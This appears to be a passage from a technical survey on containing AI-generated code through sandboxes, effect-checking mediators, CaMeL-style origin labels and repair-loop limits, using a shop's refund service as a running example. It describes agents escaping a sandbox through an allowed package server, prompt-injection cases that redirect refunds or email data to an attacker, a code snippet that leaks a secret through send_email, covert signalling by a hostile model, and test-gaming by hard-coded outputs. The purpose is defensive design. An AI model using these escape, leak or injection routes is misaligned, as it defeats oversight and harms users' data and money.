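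Generated code can reach every service on its sandbox's allow-list. OpenAI reports that in July 2026 an internal package service that its test sandboxes were allowed to use became its agents' main route to the internet. An assessor can check for such routes in the component graph by assuming that the generated code runs inside each permitted service, with all of that service's connections and credentials. If a search of the graph then reaches payments without passing through the policy check, containment depends on that service having no exploitable flaw.

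For example, suppose the refund sandbox can download packages from a server inside the shop. If that server can reach the internet and the shop's internal network, the search will reach both. Including the packages in the image removes the connection. If the server has to stay, it should hold no valuable credentials, accept no uploads and have only the connections it needs. After the incident, OpenAI added two separate layers of network isolation, one at the sandbox and one in the surrounding infrastructure, and began to isolate, restrict or replace the services that remain reachable.

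Finally, nothing outside the sandbox may trust or execute files or any other output from inside it. According to OpenAI's report, in the same incident, servers at Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets, processed files the agents had written and ended up running the agents' commands. A spreadsheet can contain formulas, a web page can contain scripts, and Python's pickle format for stored objects can run code when a program loads it. The refund service avoids these formats by accepting only a short JSON list of numbers. Its fixed code must still reject malformed lists and must never pass any part of a list to a command line or an evaluator.

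### What a sandbox guarantees, and what it cannot detect

With these settings, the shop can state a guarantee of effect. Whatever program the model writes, a run reads only the supplied orders and software, affects the outside only through a list of at most 100 KB, and ends within ten seconds. The guarantee assumes that the monitor, the host's kernel and the processor isolate the virtual machine correctly, that the host applies the settings, and that the receiving program treats the list as data. It does not cover leaks through timing or shared hardware, which Wang and Zheng as well as Andronchik and Lokhmakov exclude from their threat models.

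The sandbox also does not guarantee that customer messages remain secret. The code cannot read them, but the model read them when it wrote the code, so a hostile model could include their content in the code as a constant and signal it through which refunds the code issues.

Dividing a task between several sandboxes limits what each part can do. With Sandlock, one stage can read private data without a network connection and pass its result to another stage that has a connection but no access to the data. Wang and Zheng point out that this restricts what each stage can reach but not what passes between them. Hostile code that controls the first stage can still influence what the second receives and sends.

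The refund list has the same weakness. A refund of 50 euros for order 1182, which arrived early, is a permitted call with the wrong argument. No sandbox setting can distinguish it from a correct refund for a late order.

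## Checking each effect and the data behind it before it happens

The component that makes the payment can refuse a refund for a parcel that arrived early only if it compares the proposed refund with something the generated code did not supply, such as the original request or the shop's own records. If neither shows whether the refund is due, it can at least check where the values in the proposal came from.

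### A disk write, step by step

Hu and colleagues work out the comparison for their model-written device drivers, which turn the operating system's requests into commands for a disk. Because a driver may be hostile, it has no access to the disk and can only exchange messages with a mediator. Only the mediator can send commands to the disk.

The mediator holds a short specification of each operation. For a write, the kernel's request fixes the block address, the length and the memory area containing the data. For example, the request might be to write memory buffer B to the eight blocks starting at block 100. The driver chooses only which free slot in the disk's command queue to use.

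1. Observe: the driver asks which slots are free. The mediator answers and adds a token that the driver cannot forge. The token belongs to this request and this answer, and it expires.
2. Propose: the driver submits one command together with the token. In this case the driver is faulty or hostile, and proposes to write buffer B to the eight blocks starting at block 200.
3. Validate: the mediator takes a lock, so that nothing changes during the check, and rejects a token that is used, expired or out of date. Then it compares the command with the kernel's request, of which it kept its own copy. The request says 100 and the command says 200, so the mediator refuses, and nothing reaches the disk.
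4. Commit: if the command had matched, the mediator would have sent it, read the disk's actual response and recorded both in a log. The specification lists the possible responses (success, an error or a partial write) and what each one means for the request, so the mediator needs no further information from the driver.

Neither the hardware's memory protection nor a monitor that looks only for illegal commands would catch this error, because block 200 is a legal address and buffer B is the right buffer. A test suite would find the error only if it happened to use that address. Validation uses up the token whether the mediator accepts or refuses the proposal, so unless there is a crash, the driver cannot get two writes out of one request by repeating its proposal.

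### Committed-trace safety

Hu and colleagues call the resulting guarantee committed-trace safety, which means that the effects the mediator has committed always form the beginning of a sequence the specification allows. If the specification allows only a write to block 100 followed by a flush, which forces the data into permanent storage, the mediator may have committed nothing, just the write, or the write and then the flush. It cannot have committed the flush alone or a write to block 200. This is a safety property, so it still holds if the driver stops halfway.

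Besides a correct specification, no way around the mediator and a stated account of crashes, it depends on these assumptions:

- The program that interprets the specification is correct.
- The routines that carry out an approved command do exactly what the command says.
- The mediator commits one effect at a time.
- It knows every response that the device can give.

A proof about the driver's code, by contrast, would cover only one version, so each rewrite by the model would require a new proof.

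The proposal is only a position paper, with no implementation or measurements, so nobody yet knows how much delay the lock would add, how often a proposal would be out of date by the time the mediator checked it, or how large the mediator would become. Hu and colleagues say it is fair to doubt whether the overhead would be acceptable for drivers.

### Six conditions for mediation

A mediator can check an effect only if it can determine the effect's purpose. Hu and colleagues show this by comparing device commands with the raw block writes of a file system. A file system turns an operation such as "create a directory" into several writes to numbered blocks, and a mediator below the file system would receive only those writes.

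| Condition | Device command | Raw block write |
|---|---|---|
| Legibility: one effect shows which operation it belongs to. | The command itself names the operation, such as a write. | The same write could create a directory, remove one, rename one or corrupt the disk. |
| Observable inputs: the mediator sees everything the decision depends on. | The mediator knows which memory the caller may use. | Permission to create a directory depends on the user's credentials, which never reach this level. |
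| Correlatability: the mediator can group effects by operation and put them in order. | One command is one complete transaction. | Writes from simultaneous operations arrive mixed together and without labels. |

Better engineering cannot supply the missing information. To reconstruct the operations from block writes, a mediator would need its own version of much of the file system it is supposed to check. Hu and colleagues therefore advise placing the mediator at the same level as the operations in the specification. For a file system, this is the interface that receives "create a directory" together with the user's credentials. Mediation is possible there but has a high overhead, because the mediator has to track all the names and a checksum for each file.

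Three further conditions depend on how the designer builds the system around the mediator. Completeness means every outside change goes through the mediator. A disk that can write directly into the computer's memory violates this unless the hardware restricts it to approved buffers. Enumerable outcomes means the mediator has a full list of the responses an effect can produce, because otherwise it cannot reliably determine what happened. Explicit durability means saving data permanently is a separate effect. A disk may report success once it has received the data, even if the data would not survive a power cut, so the driver has to propose a flush and the mediator has to receive the disk's confirmation.

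### The refund service's mediator

The payment component of the refund service has so far enforced two limits. It can also check each refund against the order record, with a specification like this:

```
operation REFUND
observe   late orders that have had no refund
permit    order in this set               -- the code's choice
          amount = min(delivery_fee, 50)  -- from the order record
outcome   paid, refused, unknown
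```

Suppose a customer paid 48 euros for the delivery of a wardrobe that came late, and the generated code misplaces a decimal point and proposes a refund of 480 euros. The mediator calculates 48 from the order record and rejects the proposal. The 50-euro limit would also have stopped this refund, but not a refund of 49 euros for a delivery fee of 4.90. The comparison with the record stops both. The mediator also rejects any refund for order 1182, because that parcel was early and the order is not in the permitted set.

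The mediator can still approve a refund for the wrong order. If staff ask for refunds on last week's late parcels and the code selects one that came late a month ago, the mediator pays because the order is eligible and the amount matches the record. The disk's mediator could catch the equivalent mistake because the kernel's request named block 100, but the staff's typed request names no order that the mediator could compare with the code's choice. The shop could add two date fields to the request form and have the mediator check delivery dates against them. The code's only possible mistake on this request would then be to leave orders out. No form field would help with a request like "refund everyone whose complaint sounds justified".

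The outcome is "unknown" when the payment provider does not answer in time, so the money may or may not have left the account. The mediator should count the money as paid and refuse further proposals for that order until the provider's records show what happened.

### Effects that can be undone

Hu and colleagues distinguish irreversible effects from the recoverable ones in most earlier work on generated systems. If a model writes a database engine that returns a wrong answer, engineers can correct the engine and rerun the query, so a check after the fact is enough. But they cannot recall a sent packet or restore an overwritten disk block.

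A system can stage reversible effects. The code works on a copy, a fixed component checks the finished copy as a whole, and the system then adopts or discards it. Sandlock's temporary layer does this for files, and a database transaction does it for tables. But a staged change stays reversible only as long as nothing else acts on it. If the shop's email system reads a draft refund and emails the customer to expect the money, deleting the draft does not undo the email. The designer therefore has to keep staged data out of reach of every other component until the check is over.

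A system must check an irreversible effect before it happens. Once the shop has paid a customer 48 euros, it can ask for the money back, but this is a new request that may fail. Hu and colleagues point out that a system can hold an effect back only if something recoverable can stand in for it in the meantime. Where the task allows, the generated code should finish all its reversible work before making any payments.

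Testing code in a simulation first can also reduce the number of half-finished runs. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) describes an agent called Randori that runs and repairs its code in a simulated world, and gets the real tools only when the code works. The simulated run does not detect violations of the rules about data, however, so a real run can still stop after some of its effects have happened.

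### Tracking where a value came from

The refund mediator can recalculate the amount because the shop has a record of it. Often no such record exists, for instance when the code takes an email address from a message. The mediator can instead check where the address came from. CaMeL (Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind, 2025) does this for every value in a generated program. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes CaMeL's parts in detail.

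One model, the planner, sees the user's request but none of the data that the tools return, and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. A separate, quarantined model reads untrusted text when the program calls it. It has no tools and returns only a value of a specified type, such as a name or a date. An interpreter runs the program and labels every value with its sources and with the people who may read it. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short Python function that receives the call, its arguments and their labels, and allows or refuses the call. One policy for a simulated bank blocks a password change unless the new password comes from a trusted source.

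Suppose staff ask the refund service to "refund the delivery fee to everyone who complained today about a late parcel". This request requires reading the messages. In the style of CaMeL, the planner might write:

```python
for m in read_messages("today"):
    order = ask_quarantined("Which late order is this about?", m.text, OrderId)
    pay_refund(order)
```

One message contains the planted sentence that grants order 1182 a refund of 900 euros. The planner never receives this sentence, so the sentence cannot add a line to the program. It can only make the quarantined model return the wrong order number. The interpreter labels this number as coming from a customer's message, and a policy can then require that the message's sender placed the order.

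These labels protect against planted data that would otherwise steer the generator. They offer much less protection against a hostile planner, which can write the number 1182 directly into the program. Nikolaou and colleagues, for example, treat constants in the program as trusted. The comparison with the order record still works against a hostile planner, so the shop needs both checks. CaMeL also trusts the user's request, so if a member of staff pastes a customer's email into the request, any sentence planted in that email reaches the planner.

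Checking where data came from can also help prevent accidental errors. In *Language-Based Agent Control*, Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026) had an agent write bibliographies in which every entry had to come from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. They used Haskell's type system, much as LACUNA uses capture checking. The function that saves an entry accepts only values of a special type, and only the function that fetches entries from DBLP can create them. None of the agent's 925 citations had a wrong author, year or identifier. An agent that searched the web and wrote the entries itself got 19 of 1,002 wrong.

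### The code-then-execute pattern

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) places CaMeL in a family of designs based on the principle that once a model has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any action that matters. In the plan-then-execute pattern, the model fixes a list of tool calls before it reads any data. The dual LLM pattern, which Willison proposed in 2023, separates a model with tools from a model that reads untrusted text. The code-then-execute pattern combines the two ideas and replaces the list with a program that can contain loops and branches. Debenedetti, a co-author of the paper, built CaMeL on this pattern and added the labels and policies.

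Their example shows what the pattern does without labels. A user asks an assistant to send today's schedule to their boss. The program reads the calendar, has a model format the entries and emails the result to a fixed address. Text planted in a calendar entry cannot change the address or add another email, but it can rewrite the whole message to the boss.

The pattern's protection also depends on the program that the planner writes. When Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL without its policies, one task was to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planner fixed the program in advance, as the pattern requires, but wrote a loop with a branch for each available tool, so the file's text determined which tools ran. Two attacks succeeded this way.

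### Results on AgentDojo

AgentDojo tests agents on 97 office tasks in four simulated settings (banking, Slack, travel and a general workspace), with and without planted instructions. The 2025 survey *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* reports that, in its original evaluation, CaMeL stopped nearly all attacks with "comparable task performance". Four groups have since rerun CaMeL. Garby and colleagues ran the banking tasks three times each, Zhou and colleagues ran the Slack tasks, and *SecureClaw* (2026) and Nikolaou and colleagues used all 97. The table gives the number of tasks CaMeL completed when nobody attacked it.

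| Rerun | Tasks | With policies | Without policies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Garby and colleagues, two models | 48 runs of 16 tasks | 18 with each model | 32 and 34 |
| Zhou and colleagues, four models | 21 | 4 to 6 | 13 to 17 |
| *SecureClaw* | 97 | 29 | – |
| Nikolaou and colleagues, Claude Haiku 4.5 | 97 | 49 | – |

With CaMeL's policies on, no attack succeeded in any rerun that tested attacks, but CaMeL completed only about a fifth to a half of the ordinary tasks, so "comparable" is too generous for this configuration. The exact numbers are somewhat uncertain because none of the groups had much reason to tune CaMeL for the best result. Nikolaou and colleagues extend it, and the other three groups present rival systems. Garby and colleagues' figures also have wide margins of error because they come from only 16 different tasks. Still, the two groups that compared CaMeL with and without policies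 both found that it completed far fewer tasks with them on.

The perfect security score is weaker evidence for the policies than it seems, because most attacks failed without them too. With the policies off, 5 of 622 completed attack runs succeeded in Garby and colleagues' reruns, and none succeeded in Zhou and colleagues' reruns. One reason is that in 97 of the 144 combinations of banking task and attack, the attack needs a tool call that a program for the task would never contain, so separating the planner from the data is enough to stop it.

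Zhou and colleagues therefore built a harsher test for their own system. Whenever one of its models read a planted instruction, they replaced the model's task with that instruction, as if the attack had fully succeeded. Up to 42% of the attacks achieved their goal without policies, depending on the model, compared with none of 2,940 when policies were on. The zero count comes after a manual review discounted 29 runs that the benchmark had scored wrongly. This is much better evidence that policies matter, though it comes from a different system than CaMeL.

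### Rules that cover the whole program

CaMeL checks each call against its policies just before the call runs, so a task may fail at its last step after many earlier ones have taken effect. CaMeLoT, an extension by Nikolaou and colleagues, checks the planner's program before it starts. It translates the program into a finite set of states and transitions, then uses a standard model checker to look for a path that breaks a rule. CaMeLoT could fully check 22 of CaMeL's 28 policies for AgentDojo. The other six depend on facts known only at run time, such as who can currently read a shared file.

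The check can also enforce rules such as "every incident ticket that the program opens must later be resolved or passed on". A checker that examines every path through the program can reject a plan that omits the last step, while a monitor that can only stop a run cannot enforce this rule. But the check shows only that the program calls the tool that resolves the ticket, and that call may fail.

In a test with seven hand-made unsafe plans, CaMeLoT rejected all seven and a simplified version of CaMeL rejected one. Nikolaou and colleagues chose the rules to go beyond what CaMeL can express, so the test shows what the extension adds but not how often real plans need it. CaMeLoT also rejects some safe programs because it assumes that a loop may run any number of times.

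### Where the labels get lost

A check on origin is only as good as the labels, and Garby and colleagues found several ways to lose them in CaMeL. When a program inserts an untrusted value into a longer piece of text, the result counts as trusted. A less obvious gap arises from code that does not run. Suppose `ill` is a secret taken from a customer's message:

```python
quiet = True
signal = True
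if ill:
    quiet = False
if quiet:
    signal = False
if signal:
    send_email("x@example.com", "ill")
```

If the customer is ill, the program sets `quiet` to false, and the interpreter labels `quiet` as secret. The next condition fails, so the line that changes `signal` never runs. `signal` keeps its original value and has no secret label, so the policy allows the email. If the customer is not ill, the program sends nothing. The recipient can therefore tell whether the customer is ill by whether an email arrives.

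Garby and colleagues close this gap in their own language by stopping the program when it changes a public value inside a branch that depends on a secret. They prove, with the proof assistant Lean, that secrets cannot influence public results in any program in the language, except by affecting whether the program finishes. In CaMeL, that leak can grow because the loop that retries failed programs lies outside the part that tracks labels. A program can fail or succeed depending on one bit of the secret, and repeated attempts can reveal the rest. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) also recommends replacing the restricted Python with a small dedicated language, because features such as exceptions make information hard to track.

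Labels can also get lost between agents. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) connected three agents, each protected by CaMeL without additional policies. The user asked for a summary of job applicants to be sent to a colleague, Julie, on Slack. The first agent fetched the data through the second, then passed the summary to the third in an ordinary sentence asking it to send the summary to Julie. The summary contained an instruction planted in the database, so the third agent received that instruction as part of its trusted request. Its planner then added a line of code that emailed the applicants' data to the attacker.

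Their solution, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and data through separate channels, so the receiving planner never reads the data. On their multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of cases without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. The standard attacks rarely exploit the weakness that remains with CaMeL in each agent, but an attacker who knows about it can. The refund service would have the same weakness if a support agent summarised complaints and included the summary in its instructions to a payment agent.

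### When untrusted text chooses a permitted value

Some tasks require untrusted text to determine an effect. In AgentDojo's banking setting, a user asks the agent to pay a bill stored in a file. If an attacker replaces the file with a different bill, paying it is still what the user asked for. The program is correct, and the label correctly identifies the file as the source of the account number. Garby and colleagues report that this kind of attack also succeeded in CaMeL's original evaluation, where Debenedetti and colleagues placed it outside their threat model.

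A strict policy would refuse every payment based on a file, including legitimate ones. Randori instead lets the planner declare, before any data arrives, that the program will trust a particular value. This option raised the number of completed runs from 30 to 36 of 48 with one model and from 26 to 31 with another. It also let two attacks succeed in 1,296 runs, both using the replaced bill.

A designer can limit what untrusted text can influence. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest letting the quarantined model return only a yes or no for each document. To find this month's invoices, for example, a model looks at one file at a time and answers whether it is an invoice. Malicious text in a file can then get that file included, but it cannot affect whether any other file is included.

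The same approach works well for the refund service. If a refund requires that the order belongs to the sender of the message, arrived late and hasn't already been refunded, the planted sentence can trigger only a refund the customer was owed anyway. But if staff ask for refunds only when the delay caused serious trouble, a customer can invent the trouble. The claim would be correctly labeled as coming from the customer, but checking its origin cannot establish whether it is true.

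### The cost of writing policies

Someone has to write all these rules. For AgentDojo's four small settings, CaMeL needs policies for 28 tools that have effects and rules for labelling the output of 46 others. *SPA* (2026) points out that the guarantee depends on each policy being correct and complete. Mistakes are easy to miss because a mediator enforces wrong rules as reliably as correct ones. Peters-Gill and colleagues ran their experiments without policies, partly because any choice of policies would have been arbitrary.

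A single rule for all tools is easier to review, but it refuses more actions. For example, it might bar an agent from any action that matters once the agent has read anything untrusted. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) compares this kind of rule with a policy that depends on the origin of each argument. The more detailed policy still allowed some actions after the agent had read untrusted text, because their arguments came from acceptable sources.

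Designers can also send refused calls to a person instead of ending the task. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes Prudentia, an agent that asks for approval only when a call fails the policy check, and that plans its work to avoid such calls. It needed fewer approvals than an earlier system with similar checks and completed about as many tasks or more. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) adds that Prudentia separates trusting a piece of data from approving an action, so a person can approve one payment without marking the whole file as trusted. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues warn that tired reviewers approve unsafe actions, so asking fewer questions also makes each answer more reliable.

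Writing and checking policies takes more work as the number of tools grows. The refund service has one tool with an effect and two sources of data, the order records and the messages, so one policy and two labels are enough, and the shop can review them in full. A general assistant with access to email, files and payments needs a policy for every tool that can do harm, and its developers have to recheck the existing policies whenever they add a tool or data source.

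## Ordering the checks and limiting repair

The generated code may have to pass a parser, a type checker and a trial run in the sandbox before the refund service's payment component receives any proposals. If the code fails one of these staged checks, a repair loop can return the reason to the model and ask for new code. The number of repairs affects how often wrong code runs, while the order of the checks mostly affects how long they take.

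### The cheapest order

Every program has to pass all the checks, so their order doesn't change which programs get through. It does change the cost, because a rejected program skips the remaining checks. Paranjape, Mandal and Sun (2026), in *Optimality of Sequential Filtering Under Independent Cost and Selectivity Models*, prove that for independent checks the expected cost is lowest in ascending order of cost divided by probability of rejection. This ratio is the average amount spent per rejected program. Suppose the refund service's checks have these figures:

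| Check | Cost | Programs rejected | Cost ÷ probability |
|---|---|---|---|
| Parse | 1 ms | 5% | 20 ms |
| Type check | 400 ms | 9% | 4,444 ms |
| Trial run in the sandbox | 3,000 ms | 20% | 15,000 ms |

In this order, the type checker receives only the 95% of programs that parse, and the trial run only those that pass both earlier checks. The expected cost per program is:

1 + 0.95 × 400 + 0.95 × 0.91 × 3,000 ≈ 2,975 ms

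In reverse order, it is:

3,000 + 0.80 × 400 + 0.80 × 0.91 × 1 ≈ 3,321 ms

The saving is only about 10%, because 69% of the programs pass all three checks and cost 3,401 ms in any order.

The proof compares two neighbouring checks. With the type check before the trial run, the pair takes an average of 400 + 0.91 × 3,000 = 3,130 ms per program that reaches it. With the trial run first, the pair takes 3,000 + 0.80 × 400 = 3,320 ms. The same share of programs passes both checks in either order, so swapping them doesn't affect the time spent on any other check. Any order that breaks the rule contains two neighbouring checks in the wrong order, and swapping them reduces the total time. Repeated swaps lead to the order in the table.

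Paranjape and colleagues also ran 500 simulations with 50 filters each, in which the rule never cost more than sorting by cost alone or by pass rate alone. But they made the simulated filters independent, so the result confirms the algebra but is weak evidence about real checks, which overlap. For example, many type errors would also crash the trial run, so the trial rejects fewer programs if the type checker has already removed the ones with those errors. A designer should measure each check's rejection rate on the programs that actually reach it, and measure again after changing the order.

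### Nothing runs before the sandbox is in place

The rule's one constraint is that no generated code may execute before its confinement is active. The 3,000 ms for the trial run must therefore include starting the sandbox. The constraint also covers module imports and Rust build scripts.

It can be worth finishing all security checks before the trial run. Suppose the shop adds a scan for suspicious calls that takes 300 ms and rejects 1% of programs. Its ratio is 30,000 ms, so the rule puts it last. But if the sandbox has an undiscovered flaw, a scan after the trial run would come too late to stop a program that exploits it. Moving the scan forward adds about 26 ms per program, a small delay for a second barrier against a hostile generator.

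### Generating once: Compiled AI

Trooskens, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Compiled AI*, describe a system that generates the code for a company workflow once, checks it and then reuses it. The user specifies the workflow in a structured file. A fixed program selects tested templates and modules, and the model writes only the business logic, in functions of 20 to 50 lines. The result goes through four stages:

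- Security: scanners look for known weaknesses, such as commands assembled from untrusted input.
- Syntax: a parser, a type checker and a linter examine the code.
- Execution: the code runs on test inputs in a sandbox.
- Accuracy: a fixed program compares the outputs with known correct answers.

The ordering rule would put parsing first, since it takes almost no time and a scanner can do little with code that doesn't parse. But if the system generates the code only once, a few wasted milliseconds hardly matter.

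In a test on 400 function-calling tasks, where the code must choose the right function and arguments for a request, 384 programs passed. The other 16 ran without errors but gave wrong answers, and only the accuracy stage rejected them. Trooskens and colleagues report that the passing programs were 100% reliable. If the accuracy stage and the final score used the same expected answers, any program that passed would have to score 100%. The static security check was weaker. It caught 15 of 20 vulnerable programs and flagged none of the 20 harmless ones.

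The published pseudocode has a gap that an assessor should look for in any repair loop. When a program fails a stage, the loop asks the model for new code and sends it straight to the next stage. A program that replaces one rejected by the security scan is therefore never scanned. If the accuracy stage rejects a program, the loop returns the replacement unchecked. Trooskens and colleagues write elsewhere that every program must pass all four stages, so their implementation may differ from the pseudocode.

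A designer can prevent this mistake by making each generation and its checks one indivisible step. The workflow moves on only when the new code has passed every check, starting from the first. A failure changes only the attempt count and the error message for the model. This also limits the work, since a workflow with 5 such steps and at most 3 attempts per step calls the model at most 15 times, whatever the model writes.

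### Generating for every request: TOOLPRO

*Beyond Static Endpoints* (Liu, Li and colleagues, 2026) presents TOOLPRO, in which a model writes a new program for each request to a web service. The program can contain loops and branches, and the service runs it near its own data.

1. On the user's side, the model writes a program in Rust. A quick check looks for the necessary calls, the expected loops and conditions, and a plausible flow of values between calls.
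2. The server projects the program into a permitted subset. It rewrites every outside call to go through one function, labels the call as a read or a write, removes or replaces unsupported imports, and rejects whatever else lies outside the subset.
3. The server compiles the result to WebAssembly and runs it. The program can reach the outside only through that one function.
4. If compilation or the run fails, a model repairs the code using the compiler's messages or a record of the run, and the server projects, compiles and runs it again. After a fixed number of attempts, the system goes back to ordinary tool calls, one at a time.

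Projection can change the program, so a check of the model's original text does not cover the code that runs. Later checks and any human approval have to apply to the projected version.

TOOLPRO logs completed writes so that a repaired program doesn't make the same changes twice. Suppose refund code pays orders 1101, 1102 and 1103, then crashes on order 1104 because that order's fee is missing. When the repaired program restarts and requests the payment for order 1101, the runtime returns the logged result without paying again. It does the same for the next two orders and makes its first new payment for 1104. The runtime always resends reads because they are safe to repeat.

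If the repaired program changes the amount for order 1101 or the order of the completed payments, TOOLPRO stops using the log and falls back to separate calls. Liu and colleagues prove that no completed write happens twice as long as repairs keep the earlier writes unchanged. The proof doesn't cover a payment that went through but whose confirmation got lost, because it never enters the log. Giving each payment a unique number solves this problem, because the payment provider can use the number to ignore repeats. The fallback also needs the log, because otherwise the model might pay the first three customers again through separate calls.

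On three realistic workflows, TOOLPRO took an average of 17.9 seconds, compared with 30.2 for separate calls, and raised the share of tasks completed correctly from 60% to 93%. These results are encouraging, but the tests were small, with about 15 runs. When Liu and colleagues switched the log off, 3 of 15 runs ended in the fallback, compared with none when it was on.

In a separate breakdown, writing the program took between 7 and 8 seconds, compiling it a little over 5 and running the sandbox about 2.5. For a short task, this overhead can exceed the savings. TOOLPRO therefore estimates the benefit before it decides:

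time saved = (N − 1) × (network delay + model's decision time) − time to build the program

If building a program takes 13 seconds and each separate call adds 2 seconds of delay and decision time, the program is faster than separate calls for eight or more calls. In a test with eight calls, separate calls were about a second faster on a 1-millisecond connection, but the program was 13 seconds faster when each round trip took 2 seconds.

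### Once or for every request

Generating code once saves tokens only if the task recurs. For the function-calling tasks, Compiled AI used 9,600 tokens to generate the code and none to run it, while asking the model directly used 552 tokens each time. The token totals are equal after about 17 runs. A stored program also can't interpret free text by itself. On a set of 5,680 invoices, a version that used only fixed text patterns extracted 20.3% of the key fields correctly. A version whose stored code called a model at fixed points reached 80.0%, the same as asking the model directly.

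The two approaches also distribute errors differently. Suppose 1% of generated programs are wrong and pass every check. Over 1,000 requests, both approaches produce 10 wrong results on average. If the service generates a program for each request, the wrong results are scattered among the requests. If it generates one program and reuses it, there is a 99% chance of no wrong results and a 1% chance that all 1,000 are wrong. The reused program's errors are easier to prevent, because an hour spent reviewing it comes to 3.6 seconds per request, but they do more damage if nobody reviews it.

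Generating code in advance also keeps later customers' messages out of the prompt, so they cannot influence the code. But stored code can become wrong when the data it uses changes. If the shop switches its delivery fees from euros to cents, a program that was correct before the switch will overpay after it. The service therefore has to rerun the accuracy checks whenever the format or meaning of its data changes.

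The refund service could use both reviewed programs and code generated at run time. A weekly request for late deliveries needs only new dates, so one reviewed program is enough. A request for parcels that arrived late in one region during a strike may never recur, so the service has to generate code for it at run time.

### Why retries weaken an imperfect check

Letting the model retry until its code passes the check makes a pass more likely, but code that passes can still be wrong. If each attempt passes with probability p, the probability that none of n attempts passes is (1 − p)<sup>n</sup>, which approaches zero as n grows.

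Suppose a task is so hard that only 5% of attempts are right. The check accepts all of these, but also 10% of the wrong ones. Each attempt has a 5% chance of being right and accepted, and a 9.5% chance (0.95 × 0.10) of being wrong and accepted. In the remaining 85.5% of cases, the check rejects the code and the model tries again.

| Attempts allowed | Right code runs | Wrong code runs | Nothing runs |
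|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 5.0% | 9.5% | 85.5% |
| 3 | 12.9% | 24.6% | 62.5% |
| Unlimited | 34.5% | 65.5% | 0% |

The chance of running wrong code within n attempts is:

0.095 ÷ 0.145 × (1 − 0.855<sup>n</sup>)

In every row, about 66% of the accepted programs are wrong, so the check is no worse at the third attempt than at the first. Retries cause a program to run in cases where none would have, and for this task that program is usually wrong. In a payment system, running no program is much better than running a wrong one.

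Allowing the model more attempts requires a stricter check. To accept wrong code on fewer than 1% of requests, a check could let through about 1.05% of wrong programs if the model gets one attempt, but only 0.37% if it gets three.

On an easier task, retries do more good than harm. If 80% of attempts are right and the check is the same, allowing unlimited attempts instead of one raises the chance of running right code from 80% to 97.6%, and the chance of running wrong code only from 2% to 2.4%. The retry limit should therefore depend on how well the model does the particular task. When LACUNA's compiler rejected 89% of a weak model's code for one set of tasks, a stronger model would have helped more than more retries.

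### When feedback teaches the model to pass

These calculations assume independent attempts, meaning that each new program has the same chance of being right, and the same chance of passing if wrong, whatever happened before. In practice, a model that has misunderstood the request often makes the same mistake again, and then extra attempts achieve little. Useful feedback makes the second attempt more likely to be right than the first, as when the message "no column named delivery_cost" leads the model to the right column.

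Feedback can also lead the model to satisfy the check without solving the task. Suppose a test runs the refund code on a sample table and reports "expected a total of 196 euros, got 1,840". The model can correct the date comparison, or it can add a line that returns refunds of exactly 196 euros. In the hard task above, suppose the check accepts 10% of wrong programs at the first attempt, 30% at the second and 60% at the third, while only 5% of programs are right at each attempt. With a limit of three attempts, the system then runs wrong code 66% of the time, as often as it would with unlimited independent attempts.

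To limit this problem, *MuninAI* allows three repair attempts and stops earlier if the same error returns, judged by its type and location. It takes tests from the specification or from a generation step separate from the one that writes the code, because a model that can edit its own tests tends to pass by weakening them. Separate generation removes that incentive, but if the same model writes both the code and the tests, it may misread the request in the same way twice.

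The loop can repair only the errors that each language's check finds. C++ code goes through the compiler, but R code gets only a parser and a linter. Those don't detect that a plot uses the wrong column, so the loop can't repair it.

A designer can also hide the result of one check from the model. The repair loop uses the other checks, and the service runs the hidden check once, on the final program. If the program fails, the service gives up on the request. Restarting the loop would turn the hidden check into another imperfect filter with retries, even if the model never received the reason for the failure.

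The limit also has to cover repeated requests if an attacker can learn from rejections, because resubmitting a request would otherwise restart the count. An attacker can also steer the model through error messages. If the refund code fails to convert part of a customer's complaint into a number, Python's error message quotes that text, which may carry a planted instruction into the repair prompt. Returning only the error type and line number prevents this but gives the model less information for the repair.

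### Running code before it is finished

A language model writes from left to right and doesn't go back to change what it has written. EAGER, the system presented in *Executing as You Generate* (Sun, Lin and colleagues, 2026), therefore runs each complete Python statement while the model is still writing the next ones. For programs without errors, this reduced the total time by up to 37.3%. The benefit is largest when the model writes quickly and the code runs slowly.

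Early execution conflicts with any check that needs the whole program. A type checker might accept ten statements and reject the eleventh, but by then the first ten have run. EAGER saves time but gives up LACUNA's protection against such partial runs.

EAGER reduces the risk by waiting for the complete program if a statement starts a process, changes files, uses the network, depends on the clock or runs text as code. It recognises these statements by comparing names in the syntax tree with a list, by default of standard-library modules that often have outside effects. Sun and colleagues call this list conservative and write that EAGER delays any statement it cannot classify. But a list of modules to delay misses every name it does not contain. For example, Python's built-in `open` needs no module, and many data-analysis libraries can write files on their own. EAGER also only delays the statements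 on the list, because it schedules code and leaves confinement to the environment.

The two aims are compatible if the early run cannot affect anything outside the sandbox. The host starts the sandbox first and runs each statement as it arrives, but holds the output until the complete program has passed the parser, the type checker and any other check. If any check fails, the host destroys the sandbox and everything in it. This approach works for the refund code, which only returns a list, but would not work for code that makes payments as it runs. The approach also gives up the second barrier, because hostile code can attack the sandbox before any whole-program check has run.

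EAGER can also stop the model at the first error instead of letting it finish the program. On three sets of data-analysis tasks, the share of errors that models resolved was 2 to 44 percentage points higher with early stopping than when they received the complete failed program. Sun and colleagues suspect that seeing the rest of the faulty program makes the model more likely to repeat its original mistake. On a fourth set, which tests knowledge of particular library versions, stopping early usually lowered the success rate of repairs slightly, and by 15 points for one model. An error counted as resolved when it did not return, whether or not the new program gave the right answer. A repair loop can therefore score well on this measure and still produce more wrong programs that pass.

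### Reject, fall back or ask a person

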